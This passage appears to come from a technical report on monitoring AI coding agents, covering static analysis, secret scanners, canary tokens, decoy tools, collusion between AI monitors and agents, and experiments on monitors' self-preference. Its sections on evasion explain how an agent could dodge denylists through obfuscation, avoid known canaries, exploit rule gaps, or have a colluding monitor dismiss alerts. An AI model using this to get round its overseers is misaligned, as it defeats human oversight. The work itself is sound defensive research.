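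ActPlane and Tether also follow data, but only while a program runs, so they cover only what happens in that run. Static analysis can consider branches that a particular run would skip, and it can warn before anything has happened, but it works with an approximation of the program. Semgrep's free version follows taint only within a single function. The paid version can follow it between functions and, for some languages, between files. Semgrep recommends at least 8 GB of memory per processor core for analysis between files. GitHub lists other obstacles, such as library functions whose source code is unavailable and calls whose target is known only at run time. Better engineering can narrow these gaps but not close them all, since no algorithm can answer every such question about every program.

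A taint rule also depends on its author listing the right sources and sinks. Like a command list, it does not check whether the developer asked for the upload.

Static analysis is slightly more useful than command and file rules against an agent that rewrites a test. A pattern could catch the crudest version, a test that just asserts `True`, but it would miss a test that checks the wrong thing, because that test has an ordinary syntax tree.

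### A scanner in front of a tool call

Invariant Labs' *Code Validation* describes how to scan an agent's code before it runs. Invariant's guardrails are rules that check an agent's messages and tool calls. One built-in function parses Python code and lists the modules the code imports and the functions it calls. A rule can then, for example, reject any code that calls `eval`, which runs text as code.

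Another function passes the code to Semgrep. The guardrail that uses it scans the code in the arguments of each call to the Python tool and raises an error if Semgrep finds anything. In the documented example, a user asks for a simple web scraper, but the agent tries to run a script that takes typed input and runs it as an operating system command. A similar guardrail scans shell commands, and its example is a command that downloads a script and immediately runs it.

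If the agent submitted the five-line script through such a tool, and Semgrep had the taint rule above, the guardrail could stop the script before it opened the credentials file. Each finding includes a severity, so a developer could block only the serious ones. But these guardrails scan only the text inside the tool call, not programs already on the disk that the call starts. Command rules have the same gap with `npm test`.

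### Scanning for secrets

A secret scanner looks for passwords and keys in code. It is meant to catch mistakes such as an agent pasting the cloud key into the source code to fix the login. It would not flag the five-line script, which contains the name of the credentials file but none of the credentials.

Many keys are easy to recognise because the companies that issue them use a fixed format. Meli, McNiece and Reaves (2019) note in *How Bad Can It Git?* that Amazon's access key identifiers start with `AKIA` and Google's keys start with `AIza`. They wrote regular expressions for 15 types of service key and 4 types of private key, then removed unlikely matches with filters for entropy, words and patterns. They found secrets in more than 100,000 public GitHub repositories, and thousands of new secrets appeared every day. Their method was designed to be conservative, so the true numbers were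 probably higher.

Entropy measures how unpredictable a string's characters are. If pᵢ is the share of the string made up of character i, the entropy in bits per character is

H = −Σ pᵢ log₂ pᵢ.

The word `password` has eight letters, with only the `s` repeated, so its Shannon entropy is 2.75 bits per character. The string `q7Rz2LmX9vKc4TbW` has sixteen different characters, so its entropy is 4. A scanner with a threshold between these values would flag only the second string. Entropy alone is a poor detector, however, because code is full of random-looking strings that are not secret, such as identifiers and checksums.

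Passwords are harder to find. Meli and colleagues left them out of the study because a password can be almost any string. GitHub uses an AI model to detect them. *Clearer names for secret scanning detector types* (GitHub, 2026) distinguishes "patterns", which combine regular expressions with checks such as entropy, from "AI-detected secrets", which a model finds by analyzing the surrounding code. Only the patterns are non-learned detectors. In the running example, they would probably catch the cloud key, but detecting the database password might well require the model.

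A correct match can still be harmless. Meli and colleagues point out that a key written for a software test is a real key but does not need to be secret. Matching a pattern against the key alone cannot distinguish it from a key that must stay secret.

### What a scan can still prevent

The later a scan runs, the less it can prevent. A scan before execution, like Invariant's, can stop the five-line script from sending anything. A scan at commit time may come after the script has run, but it can still keep a pasted key out of the project's history, where the key would remain even if a later commit deleted it.

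GitHub offers a scan at this stage through its server for the Model Context Protocol (MCP), a standard way to give agents access to outside tools and data. As GitHub (2026) describes it, the developer asks the agent to check its changes for secrets, and the agent calls the scanning tool, which returns the location of any it finds. GitHub's scanning engine determines what is flagged, but it runs only if the agent calls the tool. A hook that ran the scan at every commit would not depend on the agent.

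The next chance to catch a secret comes when someone pushes the code to GitHub. GitHub's *What is push protection?* describes a check that blocks pushes containing a recognised secret. The check also covers calls to GitHub's MCP server that involve public repositories. The secret may already be in the history on the developer's machine, but the block keeps it out of the shared copy.

By default, anyone with write access to a repository can override this block by choosing a reason. If they choose that the secret is for tests or that the match is a false alarm, GitHub records an alert and closes it immediately. If they choose "I'll fix it later", the alert stays open. Organisations can limit who may override the block, which seems sensible where an agent uses an account with write access.

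The last scans run before the agent's work becomes part of the main project. GitHub's own coding agent, Copilot cloud agent, submits its work as a pull request, a proposed set of changes for someone to review. GitHub's documentation lists three security checks that run by default before the agent completes the request:

- CodeQL analyses the new code for security problems.
- A lookup compares newly added outside packages with a database of known malware and serious vulnerabilities.
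- Secret scanning looks for keys, tokens and other sensitive information.

An AI model also reviews the code, and the project's own tests run. If a check finds a problem, the agent tries to fix it before asking for review. A person then has to review and merge the changes, because the agent cannot approve or merge its own pull request. Administrators can switch off individual checks, and GitHub's *Configure Copilot coding agent’s validation tools* (2026) suggests doing so for projects where CodeQL takes too long.

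GitHub introduced these scans in October 2025 and extended them in June 2026 to other companies' agents, including Claude and Codex. GitHub's *Security validation for third-party coding agents* (2026) reports that the scans prevented "hundreds" of potential leaks and vulnerabilities, but it gives no count of those they missed or of false alarms.

These checks can keep a vulnerability or a pasted key out of the finished product, but they cannot undo anything the agent did while it was working. GitHub relies on other controls for that risk, such as limiting the agent's internet access. Letting the agent fix the findings is useful when the agent is cooperative. However, a clean final scan is then weaker evidence than a clean first scan, because the agent has revised its code until the scanner reported no more problems.

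### From honeypots to honeywords

Unlike a code scanner, which needs a description of bad code, a canary token needs only an object that nobody has a good reason to touch. Security teams had long used honeypots, decoy computers with no real work to do, when Augusto Paes de Barros suggested in February 2003 that accounts and documents could serve the same purpose. He called them "honeytokens". Lance Spitzner shared the suggestion with a mailing list about honeypots under the title *HoneyTokens* (2003) and developed it that July in a paper for Symantec, *Honeytokens* (2003). In one of Spitzner's examples, a hospital adds a fake medical record for "John F. Kennedy" to its database. No doctor needs the record, so anyone who opens it is probably snooping. Spitzner did not present the idea as new, and mentioned mapmakers who were said to add fictitious towns to catch copyists. Ten years later,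 *Honeywords* (Juels and Rivest, 2013) applied the idea to stolen password files.

Their scheme stores k possible passwords for each user, of which only one is real. A separate, well-protected computer, the honeychecker, holds the position of the real one in the list and raises an alarm if someone logs in with any of the others. Suppose a thief steals the file and works out every password in it. If the decoys are indistinguishable from the real password, the thief's first guess sets off the alarm with probability

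(k − 1)/k.

Juels and Rivest recommend listing k = 20 possible passwords for each account, one real and 19 decoys, so an attacker who steals the list and picks one at random has a 95% chance of picking a decoy. A separate server, the honeychecker, stores only the position of each real password in its list, so someone who broke into it alone would learn no passwords.

### Four events that set off a canary

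A decoy credential usually triggers an alert when someone tries to use it. The developer in the running example could put a fake Amazon key in an old-looking backup of a credentials file, as Zeltser recommends in *Plant Honeytokens to Detect Intrusions*. Reading or copying the key doesn't trigger an alert, but trying to log in to Amazon's cloud with it leaves an entry in a log that the token's provider monitors. With the free Canarytokens service, run by the security company Thinkst, the alert can take 2 to 30 minutes. *Honeypots for AI Agents* describes a newer tool, Snare, that raises the alert when a program on the machine loads the key, before the program contacts Amazon. A secret scanner may flag a decoy key in a genuine format as a real one, so a developer who keeps one in a repository may have to make an exception for it.

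A decoy file triggers an alert when someone reads or opens it. Spitzner proposed having the operating system's kernel watch for reads of chosen files, which would cover every program on the machine. Other decoy files, such as Word documents with a hidden link, send a signal when someone opens them. These are easier to set up, but whether they send the signal depends on the program that opens the file.

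A canary token can be a unique string, planted so that a monitor can detect it in outgoing traffic. Spitzner suggested planting a fake credit card number in a database and having a network monitor look for it. grith, a tool that checks agents' actions, documents a version for agents in *Canary tokens*. It searches for the planted string in agents' outgoing calls, including web addresses, shell commands and the names of files the agent writes. grith gives each call a risk score and denies any call above 8.0. A canary match scores 9.5, so grith blocks the call without asking the user, whereas most canaries only raise an alert.

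grith does not check the contents of a web request, so the five-line script would not set off this filter. Its documentation also warns about a problem with setup. In version 0.3.1, the command for adding a canary reports success but does not register it with the program that does the checking. A developer who did not test the decoy would have no way of knowing that it was dead.

A decoy tool triggers an alert when the agent calls it. *AgentShield* (2026) adds three fake tools to the agent's real ones, with names such as `export_all_user_data`, and checks every call before it runs. *Beyond Pattern Matching* (2026) does the same with names such as `admin_shell`, and claims that any call to one of them confirms with "one hundred percent precision" that someone has planted instructions in the agent's input. That figure follows from the assumption that no legitimate task leads the agent to call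 a decoy. But a confused agent could call one by mistake, or a user could ask the agent to open an administrator's shell. More alarming names make such calls less likely, but they also make the decoys easier for a hostile agent to recognise.

Decoys of every kind have to look real. Weinberg (2026), in *PHANTOM*, argues that decoys made from templates lack their organisation's names and conventions, and offers a generator that adds them. The reported rate of "human acceptance" rises from 6% to 100%, but no people took part. The rate comes from a formula that gives higher scores for the same organisation-specific names that the generator inserts. The argument is reasonable, but these results add little support to it.

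Some decoys aimed at AI attackers also contain hidden instructions meant to derail the attacker, but whether these work depends on how the particular model responds. For this reason, *Optional Traps* (2026) uses only ordinary fake assets and a canary credential.

### One alert, from planting to notification

Thinkst's *One for all the models out there!* describes a decoy MCP server for catching agents that explore files they should not. Suppose the developer in the running example wants to use it:

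1. The developer selects the MCP token on the Canarytokens website, enters an email address and adds a reminder of where the decoy will go. The developer also chooses whether the alert should fire when an agent connects to the server or only when it calls one of the server's tools.
2. The site generates a settings entry for a server called "cloud-auth-broker". The developer adds it to the repository's MCP settings file and disables it for their own agent, so that the agent does not connect automatically.
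3. An agent reads the settings file and connects to the server, which offers it several tools that appear to provide credentials for other services.
4. The agent calls one of them, `fetch_kubeconfig`, whose name suggests login details for a cluster of servers.
5. The developer receives an email with the agent's network address, the tool it called and the reminder from step 1.

If the developer had chosen to be alerted on connection, the email would have followed step 3. Thinkst recommends that setting for teams that do not use MCP, since nothing of theirs should connect. Teams that do use it should set the alert to fire on a tool call instead. In one of Thinkst's demonstrations, a coding agent triggered the token even though the organisation's policy had disabled MCP.

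The email shows that something read the settings file and acted on it, but not why. If the network address is the developer's own, the most likely explanation is that their own agent went beyond its task, and the next step would be to read its session log.

### Reading is weaker evidence than use

Canaries set for human intruders raise few false alarms because honest people have no reason to touch them. In the 2003 mailing-list discussion, Spitzner estimated that a honeypot might produce 5 or 10 alerts a day in an organisation whose other detectors produced 5,000. But Zeltser warns that decoy web links cause the most false alarms of any type, because people click on them and automated tools follow every link. On a shared machine, a colleague might also find a decoy key and try it in good faith.

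A coding agent breaks the assumption much more often, because reading files is part of its job and it may search a whole directory to find the cause of one failing test. *Honeypots for AI Agents* notes that a well-behaved agent may read credential files while gathering context, or decide that a credential it has found is relevant to the task. A broad text search would also open every decoy file in its path. Since agents often run under the developer's own account, a simple file monitor may not be able to tell the agent's reads from the developer's.

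A hypothetical example shows the difference between alerting when an agent reads a decoy file and alerting when it tries the decoy key. Suppose a company runs 10,000 agent sessions, ten of them harmful. Eight of the harmful sessions read the file, but so do 5% of the harmless ones, or about 500, so only about one in sixty alerts on reading would be correct. If six of the harmful sessions and two of the harmless ones go on to try the key, three in four alerts on use would be correct, but they would miss four harmful sessions instead of two.

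An alert on reading also comes earlier, possibly before any data has left the machine, and it can reveal a thief who copies the file but never tries the key. An alert on use comes later but is much easier to interpret, because an agent doesn't trigger it just by coming across the key. Even an alert on use doesn't prove malice. The agent in Anthropic's incident log was apparently trying to finish its task when it looked for other access tokens, and it could have triggered such an alert by using a decoy key. The alert would still have been useful, because nobody had given the agent permission to use what it found.

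Alerts on use seem the better default for a coding agent. Alerts on reading make more sense for files well outside the project, where the agent has no work to do. They would also produce fewer false alarms if the agent ran under its own account, as it does in Codex's Windows sandbox, because the monitor could then ignore the developer's reads.

The prototype in *Caught in the Act(ivation)* (2026) keeps the real credentials in a store that only the tools can use, and puts decoys in the text that the model reads. The agent is expected to read the decoys, so that raises no alert, but a text match raises one if a decoy appears in the agent's output. Legitimate work never needs the decoys because the tools use the real credentials. The full system adds a detector that reads the model's internal activity, so only the text match is a fixed check. The prototype does not cover credentials that an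 agent passes in the arguments of a tool call, where a coding agent would often put them.

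## What theory says about collusion and the limits of fixed rules

### Why a fixed rule cannot collude

A monitor can collude with the agent it watches only if something about the agent or its plan changes the monitor's verdict. The monitor might recognise the agent as a copy of itself, accept the agent's excuse or prefer that the agent succeed. A command rule r(c, a) can't be influenced in these ways because its only inputs are the command and its arguments. A hostile agent therefore gets the same verdict as a developer who types the same command by hand.

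Test results are also easier to trust, because a fixed rule cannot recognise a test and then behave differently in real use. (Tests reveal much less about commands that nobody thought to include.)

FORGE depends on this property. Palumbo and colleagues treat the agent as a black box that may attempt anything, and they do not model why it chose an action. Given a finite set of recorded facts, their Datalog rules always finish and give the same result. But the guarantee holds only under conditions that the rules cannot ensure. The surrounding software has to intercept every action before it takes effect and accurately record what influenced it. The policy has to express what the user wants, and it must not permit actions that would change the policy or interfere with the monitor.

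The immunity therefore covers only how the rule computes a verdict, not the people and models that write the rule or act on its alerts.

### How dependence can return

ActPlane and ClawGuard allow the agent's own model to write the rules, so collusion is still possible at that stage. A model that wanted to help later copies of itself could add an exemption that looks reasonable. An unintentional omission seems much more likely. If the model does not recognise some action as dangerous, it will not write a rule against it, and an agent built on the same model may take that action for the same reason. The rules can then miss the same dangers as the agent, even though no model decides whether an action breaks them.

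Models also make simpler mistakes, such as the structural faults in the draft rules for NOMOS. Yu and colleagues point out that a gate with "no judgment of its own" will enforce faulty rules as written. But people and software can at least inspect a written rule before the agent starts work.

A rule also fails if the agent can edit it. Schneider's *Enforceable Security Policies* (2000) notes that a program can defeat a monitor by corrupting the monitor's internal state, so the program must have no write access to that state. For a coding agent, this restriction covers the rule files, the harness's settings and any record a rule depends on, such as ActPlane's record of the last successful test run. Codex, for example, makes its settings folder read-only.

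An agent that can only read the rules cannot change a verdict, but it can predict verdicts without trying anything. How much this helps depends on the rule. If the agent knows which key is a canary, it can avoid that key, and the canary becomes useless. Knowing that the kernel blocks every read of a file, however, doesn't help the agent read it. Error messages also reveal the rules, though more slowly. ActPlane's plain-language reasons help a cooperative agent correct itself, but they would also tell a hostile agent which rule it had hit.

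A rule-based check can also come to depend on an AI model after the rule gives its verdict, if the model decides which alerts reach a person. People then learn of a harmful action only if the rule flags it and the model upholds the flag. Suppose the rule flags 40% of harmful actions and an honest model wrongly dismisses a fifth of those alerts. People learn of 32% of the harmful actions (0.4 × 0.8). If the model colludes and dismisses all of those alerts, they learn of none.

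### A weak rule or a second AI monitor

The case for fixed rules does not require them to be good detectors. Suppose an AI monitor misses 20% of harmful actions and a team can afford one more detector. It can add another AI monitor, which also misses 20%, or a fixed rule, which misses 60%. (These figures, like those in the other worked examples below, are illustrative and do not come from measurements.)

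Let q be the share that each AI monitor misses, and let φ be the correlation between their misses. The share that both miss is

q² + φ q(1 − q).

The q² term is the share of harmful actions both AI monitors would miss if their mistakes were independent, and the other term is the extra overlap in their mistakes. With q = 0.2 and φ = 0.7, the result is 0.04 + 0.7 × 0.16 = 0.152, so both monitors miss 15.2% of harmful actions. If the rule's misses are independent of the AI monitor's, the rule and one AI monitor both miss 0.2 × 0.6 = 0.12, or 12%.

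The rule is the better addition here, although by itself it misses three times as many harmful actions as the second AI monitor. An added detector helps only by catching actions that the existing monitor has missed. The second AI monitor misses 76% of those (0.152 ÷ 0.2), while the rule misses 60%, the same as its overall rate. The rule's advantage depends on a high correlation between the two AI monitors. At φ = 0.5 the two options would tie, and below that the second AI monitor would be better.

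Collusion widens the gap. If the AI monitors help the agent, they miss everything, while the rule still misses only 60%.

| Detectors | Missed by both, honest AI monitors | Missed by both, colluding AI monitors |
|---|---|---|
| Two AI monitors (φ = 0.7) | 15.2% | 100% |
| One AI monitor and one independent rule | 12% | 60% |

Even if the AI monitors colluded on only one harmful action in twenty, the AI pair would miss 19.4% overall and the mixed pair 14.4%. The 60% figure assumes that a colluding monitor does not tell the agent where the rule's gaps are. A monitor that had read the rule file could do so, which is a reason to keep the file from both the monitor and the agent.

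The 12% figure is more doubtful because it assumes that the rule misses harmful actions independently of the AI monitor. Software engineers learned in the 1980s to distrust that kind of assumption.

### Why separate work fails in the same places

Engineers who build safety-critical systems sometimes use N-version programming, in which several teams write the same program separately and the system runs all the versions and takes a majority vote. Its promised reliability depends on the versions failing independently. Knight and Leveson tested this assumption in *An Experimental Evaluation of the Assumption of Independence in Multi-Version Programming* (1986).

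They had 27 students at two universities each write a program that decides from radar data whether to launch an interceptor missile. The students worked from the same specification and were told not to discuss the project. Each program had to pass 200 test cases before it ran on a further million cases, which were the same for every program. Six programs never failed, and 23 of the 27 were right more than 99.9% of the time. But two or more programs failed together on 1,255 cases, about ten times the roughly 126 that independent failures would have produced, and on two of those cases eight programs failed.

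Some students made the same mistake when checking whether three points lie on a straight line. The points do if the angle they form is 0 or 180 degrees, but these students forgot to check for 180. The mistake made one program fail 231 times and another 37 times, and the first program also failed in all 37 of those cases.

The experiment used one fairly small problem, and Knight and Leveson warn that the result may not extend to others. Some supporters of N-version programming attacked the study, and Knight and Leveson accuse them of describing it inaccurately in *A Reply to the Criticisms of the Knight & Leveson Experiment*. Extra versions were still useful. Littlewood, Popov and Strigini (2001) report in *Modelling software design diversity* that groups of three programs that voted by majority were on average about ten times as reliable as single programs, though some groups did worse than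 some single programs.

A year before the journal paper appeared, Eckhardt and Lee (1985), in *A Theoretical Basis for the Analysis of Redundant Software*, had shown why such overlap is to be expected even if the teams never influence each other. Let θ(x) be the probability that a randomly chosen program fails on input x, which measures how hard that input is. Two separately written programs both fail on x with probability θ(x)². Averaged over all inputs, the probability that both fail is

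E[θ²] = (E[θ])² + Var(θ).

Here (E[θ])² is the probability that both programs fail if their failures are independent, and Var(θ) measures how much difficulty varies between inputs. The variance is zero only if all the inputs that arise are equally hard. Otherwise, one program's failure suggests that the input is hard, so the other program is more likely to fail too.

The effect can be large. Littlewood and colleagues give a made-up example with five possible inputs, in which a random program fails 0.58% of the time. If failures were independent, two programs would both fail about 0.003% of the time. In the example, they both fail 0.37% of the time, roughly 110 times as often.

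Eckhardt and Lee also doubt that a single correlation coefficient can capture this kind of dependence, because the chance of a shared failure varies with the input. The same caution applies to the φ of 0.7 above, which summarises one mix of harmful actions and would probably change if agents attempted different ones.

### When a rule and an AI monitor find different things hard

A rule and an AI monitor work by very different methods, so the relevant model is a later one. Littlewood and Miller (1989), in *Conceptual modeling of coincident failures in multiversion software*, allow each method its own difficulty function. For methods A and B, the probability that both fail is

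E[θ_A] E[θ_B] + Cov(θ_A, θ_B).

The covariance is positive if the same inputs tend to be hard for both methods. It is negative if inputs that are hard for one tend to be easy for the other, and both methods then fail on the same input less often than they would if their failures were independent.

Suppose half of all harmful actions are plainly written and half are disguised. The AI monitor misses 5% of the plain ones and 35% of the disguised ones, which averages 20% as before. The rule misses 25% and 95%, which averages 60%. If their misses are independent within each half, the share of harmful actions that both miss is

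½(0.05 × 0.25) + ½(0.35 × 0.95) ≈ 0.173.

That is 17.3%, worse than the 15.2% from two AI monitors, so there is no longer a reason to add the rule. This is true even though neither detector's overall miss rate has changed.

Now suppose the harmful actions divide differently. Half come with a persuasive excuse, and the AI monitor misses 35% of those and 5% of the rest. Excuses don't affect the rule, which covers a few sensitive files. The agent mostly makes excuses when it tries to access those files, so the rule misses 25% of the actions with excuses and 95% of the others. Only 6.75% of the harmful actions now get past both detectors.

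A rule is most useful where the AI monitor is weakest. Littlewood and Strigini (2004), in *Redundancy and Diversity in Security*, call this "tailored diversity": each layer of defence should be especially strong against the threats most likely to get through the others. For a coding agent, this favours putting file rules and canaries around things the agent might persuade the AI monitor to let it access, rather than adding another list of suspicious-looking commands that the monitor would have noticed anyway.

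Littlewood and Strigini also defend the use of probabilities for security against deliberate attackers, since a system's owner is uncertain about what an attacker will try next. But they add that intruders who find a hole may exploit it intensively until someone fixes it. This is a particular problem for fixed rules. A rule that misses 60% of a varied set of harmful actions may miss all of the next hundred if the agent has found a gap and keeps using it.

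The size of the real overlap has to be measured. It could well be smaller than the software experiments suggest, because a rule and an AI monitor have much less in common than two programs written to the same specification. But Littlewood and colleagues warn against assuming independence even between components that work on different principles, and they see no way to justify assuming negative correlation in a real project without evidence.

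### Model-written rules and shared gaps

The software experiments are more directly relevant to rules that AI models write. In *N-Version Programming with Coding Agents*, Ron, Baudry and Monperrus (2026) gave AI coding agents Knight and Leveson's missile specification word for word. They combined five coding tools with 23 models and three programming languages, and 48 of the 69 resulting programs passed the entry test. Out of a million cases, two or more programs failed on the same case 429 times, compared with about 115 expected if the programs failed independently. The same few bugs appeared in programs from different agents and in different languages.

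Ron and colleagues trace many of the shared failures to hard or ambiguous parts of the specification. Knight and Leveson had concluded that none of the common faults in their experiment came from flaws in the specification. Whichever view is right, a written policy for an agent is usually far less precise than that missile specification, which researchers had already debugged.

Voting still reduced the average number of failures, from 387 for a single program to 131 for a group of three. Of the 17,296 possible groups, 11,844 never failed. Having models from several companies write the rules would probably reduce the gaps in the same way, but not remove those caused by an unclear instruction. *A Systematic Methodology for Evaluating Failure Independence in LLM-Generated Code* (2026) distinguishes how differently programs are written from whether they fail on the same inputs. Only the second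 matters here, so checking that the rule sets look different would not be enough.

### One effect, many forms

Even a carefully written rule has limits that do not depend on its author. For a text matcher, one limit is the gap between a command's wording and its effect. Write e(c) for the effect of command c and B for the set of bad effects. The author of a denylist wants to block

{c : e(c) ∈ B},

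but the matcher blocks the set of commands whose text fits a pattern. Authors usually start from a familiar command and generalise from it. A shell is a programming language, and programming languages offer no end of ways to write the same operation, so the set the author wants to block is much larger than any list of familiar commands. Rewording or obfuscation can take a harmful command outside the pattern and leave its effect unchanged. An agent can also do this without meaning to, when it tries another way to finish its task after a block.

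Rules about events have a similar problem. Schneider's example is a rule against sending messages after reading a file. The rule works only if its definition of "send" covers every way the system can send a message, including those hidden deep in the system.

One remedy is to apply the rule at a point every form must pass through, as kernel rules do with system calls. Another is to check the effect instead of the wording. In one banking test, Yu and colleagues found that seven of nine attack goals depended on whether the user had named the target of the action, however the attacker phrased the request, so a rule about the target covers all seven.

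### What a scanner cannot decide

It would be better still if a scanner could read a program and work out its effects. Rice's theorem, a basic result in the theory of computation, shows that no scanner can always do this. For any property of what programs do, no algorithm can decide correctly for every program whether it has that property, unless all programs have it or none do. (Properties of a program's text are different. A scanner can easily decide whether a program contains the word `eval`.)

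Suppose we had a perfect scanner for programs that send the credentials file to an outside address. For any program P that only does calculations, we could write a new program that runs P to the end and then sends the file. The new program would send the file if and only if P finishes, so we could use the scanner to determine whether P finishes. Alan Turing proved in 1936 that no algorithm can determine this for every program, so the perfect scanner cannot exist. Cousot, Giacobazzi and Ranzato prove a version of Rice's theorem specifically for static analysis in *Program Analysis is Harder than Verification*.

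Every general scanner must therefore miss some cases, raise some false alarms or sometimes give no answer, though its designers can choose which. A scanner that blocks whatever it cannot prove safe will miss nothing within its scope but will also block harmless programs.

The theorem probably matters little for most code that agents write, which is short and conventional. If a scanner misses a problem in such code, the more likely reason is that nobody wrote the right rule. The theorem matters more when an agent is trying to hide something, because it can deliberately write a program that is difficult to analyze.

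A possible way around the difficulty is proof-carrying code, which Schneider describes. Whoever produces a program also supplies a proof that it obeys the policy, and simple software checks the proof before the program runs. Checking a proof is much easier than finding one. An agent could in principle supply the proof, and the checker would not need to trust the agent, because it would reject an invalid proof. But someone would still have to state the policy precisely.

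### What a run-time monitor can enforce

A monitor that watches a program as it runs doesn't need to predict what the program will do. Schneider asks which policies such a monitor can enforce if it can only observe the program's steps and stop the program before it breaks a rule. Firewalls, command rules for agents, and most operating-system controls work this way.

Such a monitor sees a single run, and only as far as the present moment. Write P(σ) for "run σ is acceptable". Schneider shows that an enforceable policy has to meet these conditions:

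- P judges each run by itself, without comparing it with other possible runs.
- Nothing that happens later can redeem an unacceptable run. If P(τ) is false, then P is also false for every continuation of τ.
- Every unacceptable run becomes unacceptable after a finite number of steps, so there is a point at which the monitor can act.

Policies that meet all of these are safety properties, meaning they forbid some definite bad event. One example is the rule against sending after reading, which a monitor can enforce with two states, "no file read" and "file read". The program starts in "no file read", where it may send freely. Reading a file moves it to "file read", where the monitor stops the program if it tries to send. In the running example, this would stop an agent that opened the credentials file and then tried to contact an outside service.

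"The agent must eventually fix the login" is not a safety property. However long the agent takes, it might still succeed later, so the monitor can never identify a step where the agent broke the rule.

Information flow falls outside the class for a different reason. A message reveals the database password if a different password would have led to a different message. Checking this requires knowing about other possible runs, which the monitor does not see. Schneider notes that monitors said to prevent information flow enforce a stricter policy. ActPlane's labels, for example, depend on what a program has read rather than what its message contains. Better engineering can reduce the resulting false alarms, but a monitor of this kind cannot enforce the exact policy. Monitors that can also hold back or insert actions, as Tether holds back web requests, can enforce some policies outside Schneider's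 class, but they still see only one run at a time, so the problem with information flow remains.

Monitors cannot enforce some safety properties either. A rule that an agent must answer within an hour forbids a definite bad event, but no monitor can stop time from passing, as Schneider observes of a similar rule. Basin et al. (2012) refine Schneider's account by separating actions a monitor can prevent from those it can only observe.

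The weakened test in the running example is hard to forbid for a different reason. Rewriting the test so that it always passes is a definite event, so Schneider's conditions would allow a monitor to forbid it. But the monitor would need a computable way to tell a weakened test from a corrected one. That depends on what the test does when it runs, so Rice's theorem applies again. The developer could instead forbid all edits to tests. A simple file rule can enforce this stricter policy, but it would also block honest corrections.

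Schneider's analysis is more encouraging about combining monitors. Monitors working together enforce all of their policies at once, so adding one cannot weaken the others. It can only block more actions, and in the extreme case it blocks everything the program tries to do.

### Rare harm and false alarms

When harmful actions are rare, most alerts can be mistaken even at a low false-alarm rate, and this applies to fixed detectors as much as to AI monitors. If p is the share of actions that are harmful, d the detection rate and f the false-alarm rate, the share of alerts that are correct is

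pd / (pd + (1 − p)f).

Suppose agents take a million actions, of which 100 are harmful. A detector with a 90% detection rate and a 1% false-alarm rate raises 90 correct alerts and 9,999 false ones, so fewer than one alert in a hundred is correct. A canary with a 20% detection rate and a 0.001% false-alarm rate raises 20 correct alerts and about 10 false ones, so about two in three are correct. To match that share of correct alerts, the first detector would need a false-alarm rate of about 0.0045%.

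Axelsson's *The Base-Rate Fallacy and the Difficulty of Intrusion Detection* (2000) makes the same argument about intrusion detection. In his hypothetical computer network, intrusions account for 20 of the million log records produced each day. With perfect detection and a false-alarm rate of 0.001%, about 66% of alarms are correct. If the detection rate falls to 70%, 58% are still correct, but if the false-alarm rate rises to 0.1%, only about 2% are correct, even with perfect detection. Axelsson found no experiments on how security staff respond to false alarms, but studies of power stations and factories suggested that most operators would stop trusting an alarm by the time half of its warnings were false.

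The canary in the illustration misses 80 of the 100 harmful actions, so it cannot replace the noisier detector. But at five minutes per alert, a person would need about 840 hours to check the noisier detector's alerts and only two and a half hours to check the canary's. Few teams could spare 840 hours, and many would be tempted to let an AI model sort the alerts. If they do, it makes sense to send the canary's alerts straight to a person, so that a colluding model cannot dismiss them.

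## Experiments on errors that AI monitors share with agents

The argument for pairing an AI monitor with a weak rule depended on the assumption that a second AI monitor would mostly repeat the first one's mistakes, or that both monitors might collude with the agent. Researchers have tested both assumptions, though usually by having language models grade answers or code rather than monitor agents.

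Their results are easy to confuse because a monitor can approve a harmful action for different reasons. Suppose the agent in the running example logs in with a password it was not supposed to use, and the monitor approves the login.

- The monitor may favour its own work. It would have objected if an unrelated model had done the same thing.
- It may share a blind spot with the agent. Neither model treats borrowing the password as a problem, so the monitor would approve the login whoever made it.
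- It may be covering for the agent. It recognises that the login is forbidden and reports that it is fine.

Experimenters can detect favouritism by changing who appears to have acted, and they can detect shared blind spots by comparing the monitor's errors with the agent's over many cases. It is harder to show that a monitor is covering for an agent, because that depends on what the monitor recognised before it gave its verdict.

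### One action, two apparent authors

Khullar and colleagues kept the action the same and changed where it appeared in the conversation. In the baseline, a user presented the action in a new conversation and asked the model to rate it. In a second version, the action appeared as the model's own earlier message, and the user then asked for the rating. In a third, the model produced the action and rated it in a single reply.

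The experiments used ten models from Anthropic, Google and OpenAI. In one task, the models wrote patches for real bug reports and rated each patch's correctness, and the projects' own tests showed which patches worked. In another task, planted comments had led the models to write insecure code, and the models rated its risk or decided whether to approve it. Other tasks involved scam emails and an office assistant that could leak confidential documents.

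The researchers measured detection with AUROC, here the probability that a working patch gets a higher rating than a faulty one (0.5 is chance). When GPT-5 rated its own patches in a new conversation, the AUROC was 0.99. It fell to 0.92 when the patch appeared as GPT-5's earlier message and to 0.89 when GPT-5 wrote and rated the patch in one reply. Most of the drop came from higher ratings for faulty patches. In one of the insecure-code tests, the models were five times as likely to approve a patch that appeared to be their own.

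Claude Opus 4 sometimes rated a leak of confidential documents 9 or 10 out of 10 for risk in a new conversation, but 0 when the leak appeared as its own action. Equally large shifts in the other direction were five to ten times less common.

Ratings usually stayed within half a point of each other whether the prompt attributed the patch to the model itself, another model or nobody. More reasoning did not reliably help. The effect was strongest when the model had produced the action itself, and it often disappeared when the researchers inserted another model's work into the same position. Claude Sonnet 4, for example, kept an AUROC of 0.99 on GPT-5's patches in both formats that had misled GPT-5. A developer who tests a monitor on a stored set of bad actions could therefore miss the problem.

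Seven of the ten models showed the opposite bias when they rated the harmfulness of fixed essays they had not written. On average, they were harsher on essays presented as their own. The tasks were also short and simple, and Khullar and colleagues could say little about long sessions or models that take extremely harmful actions unprompted.

Nobody trained these models to have the bias or asked them for it, but it is fairly easy to avoid. Having the monitor read the action in a separate conversation removes the cue that caused most of the shift. Teams that set up their monitor this way have one less reason to use a fixed rule.

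### How much self-preference is left after controls

Other studies test whether models favor their own output even when they judge it in a new conversation. In *Self-Preference Bias in Rubric-Based Evaluation of Large Language Models*, Pombal, Rei and Martins (2026) used criteria that ordinary software can check, such as whether a program passes a test. They divided the rate at which a judge wrongly passes its own failed outputs by the rate for failed outputs from unrelated models. A ratio of 1 means no self-preference.

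On 5,685 programming tests, the ratio was about 20 for GPT-5, 1.8 for Claude Sonnet 4.5 and close to 1 for two of the three Gemma models. On a set of simpler writing instructions, most ratios were slightly above 1, but only two were statistically significant. A majority vote of judges from five model families reduced the bias on these instructions but did not remove it.

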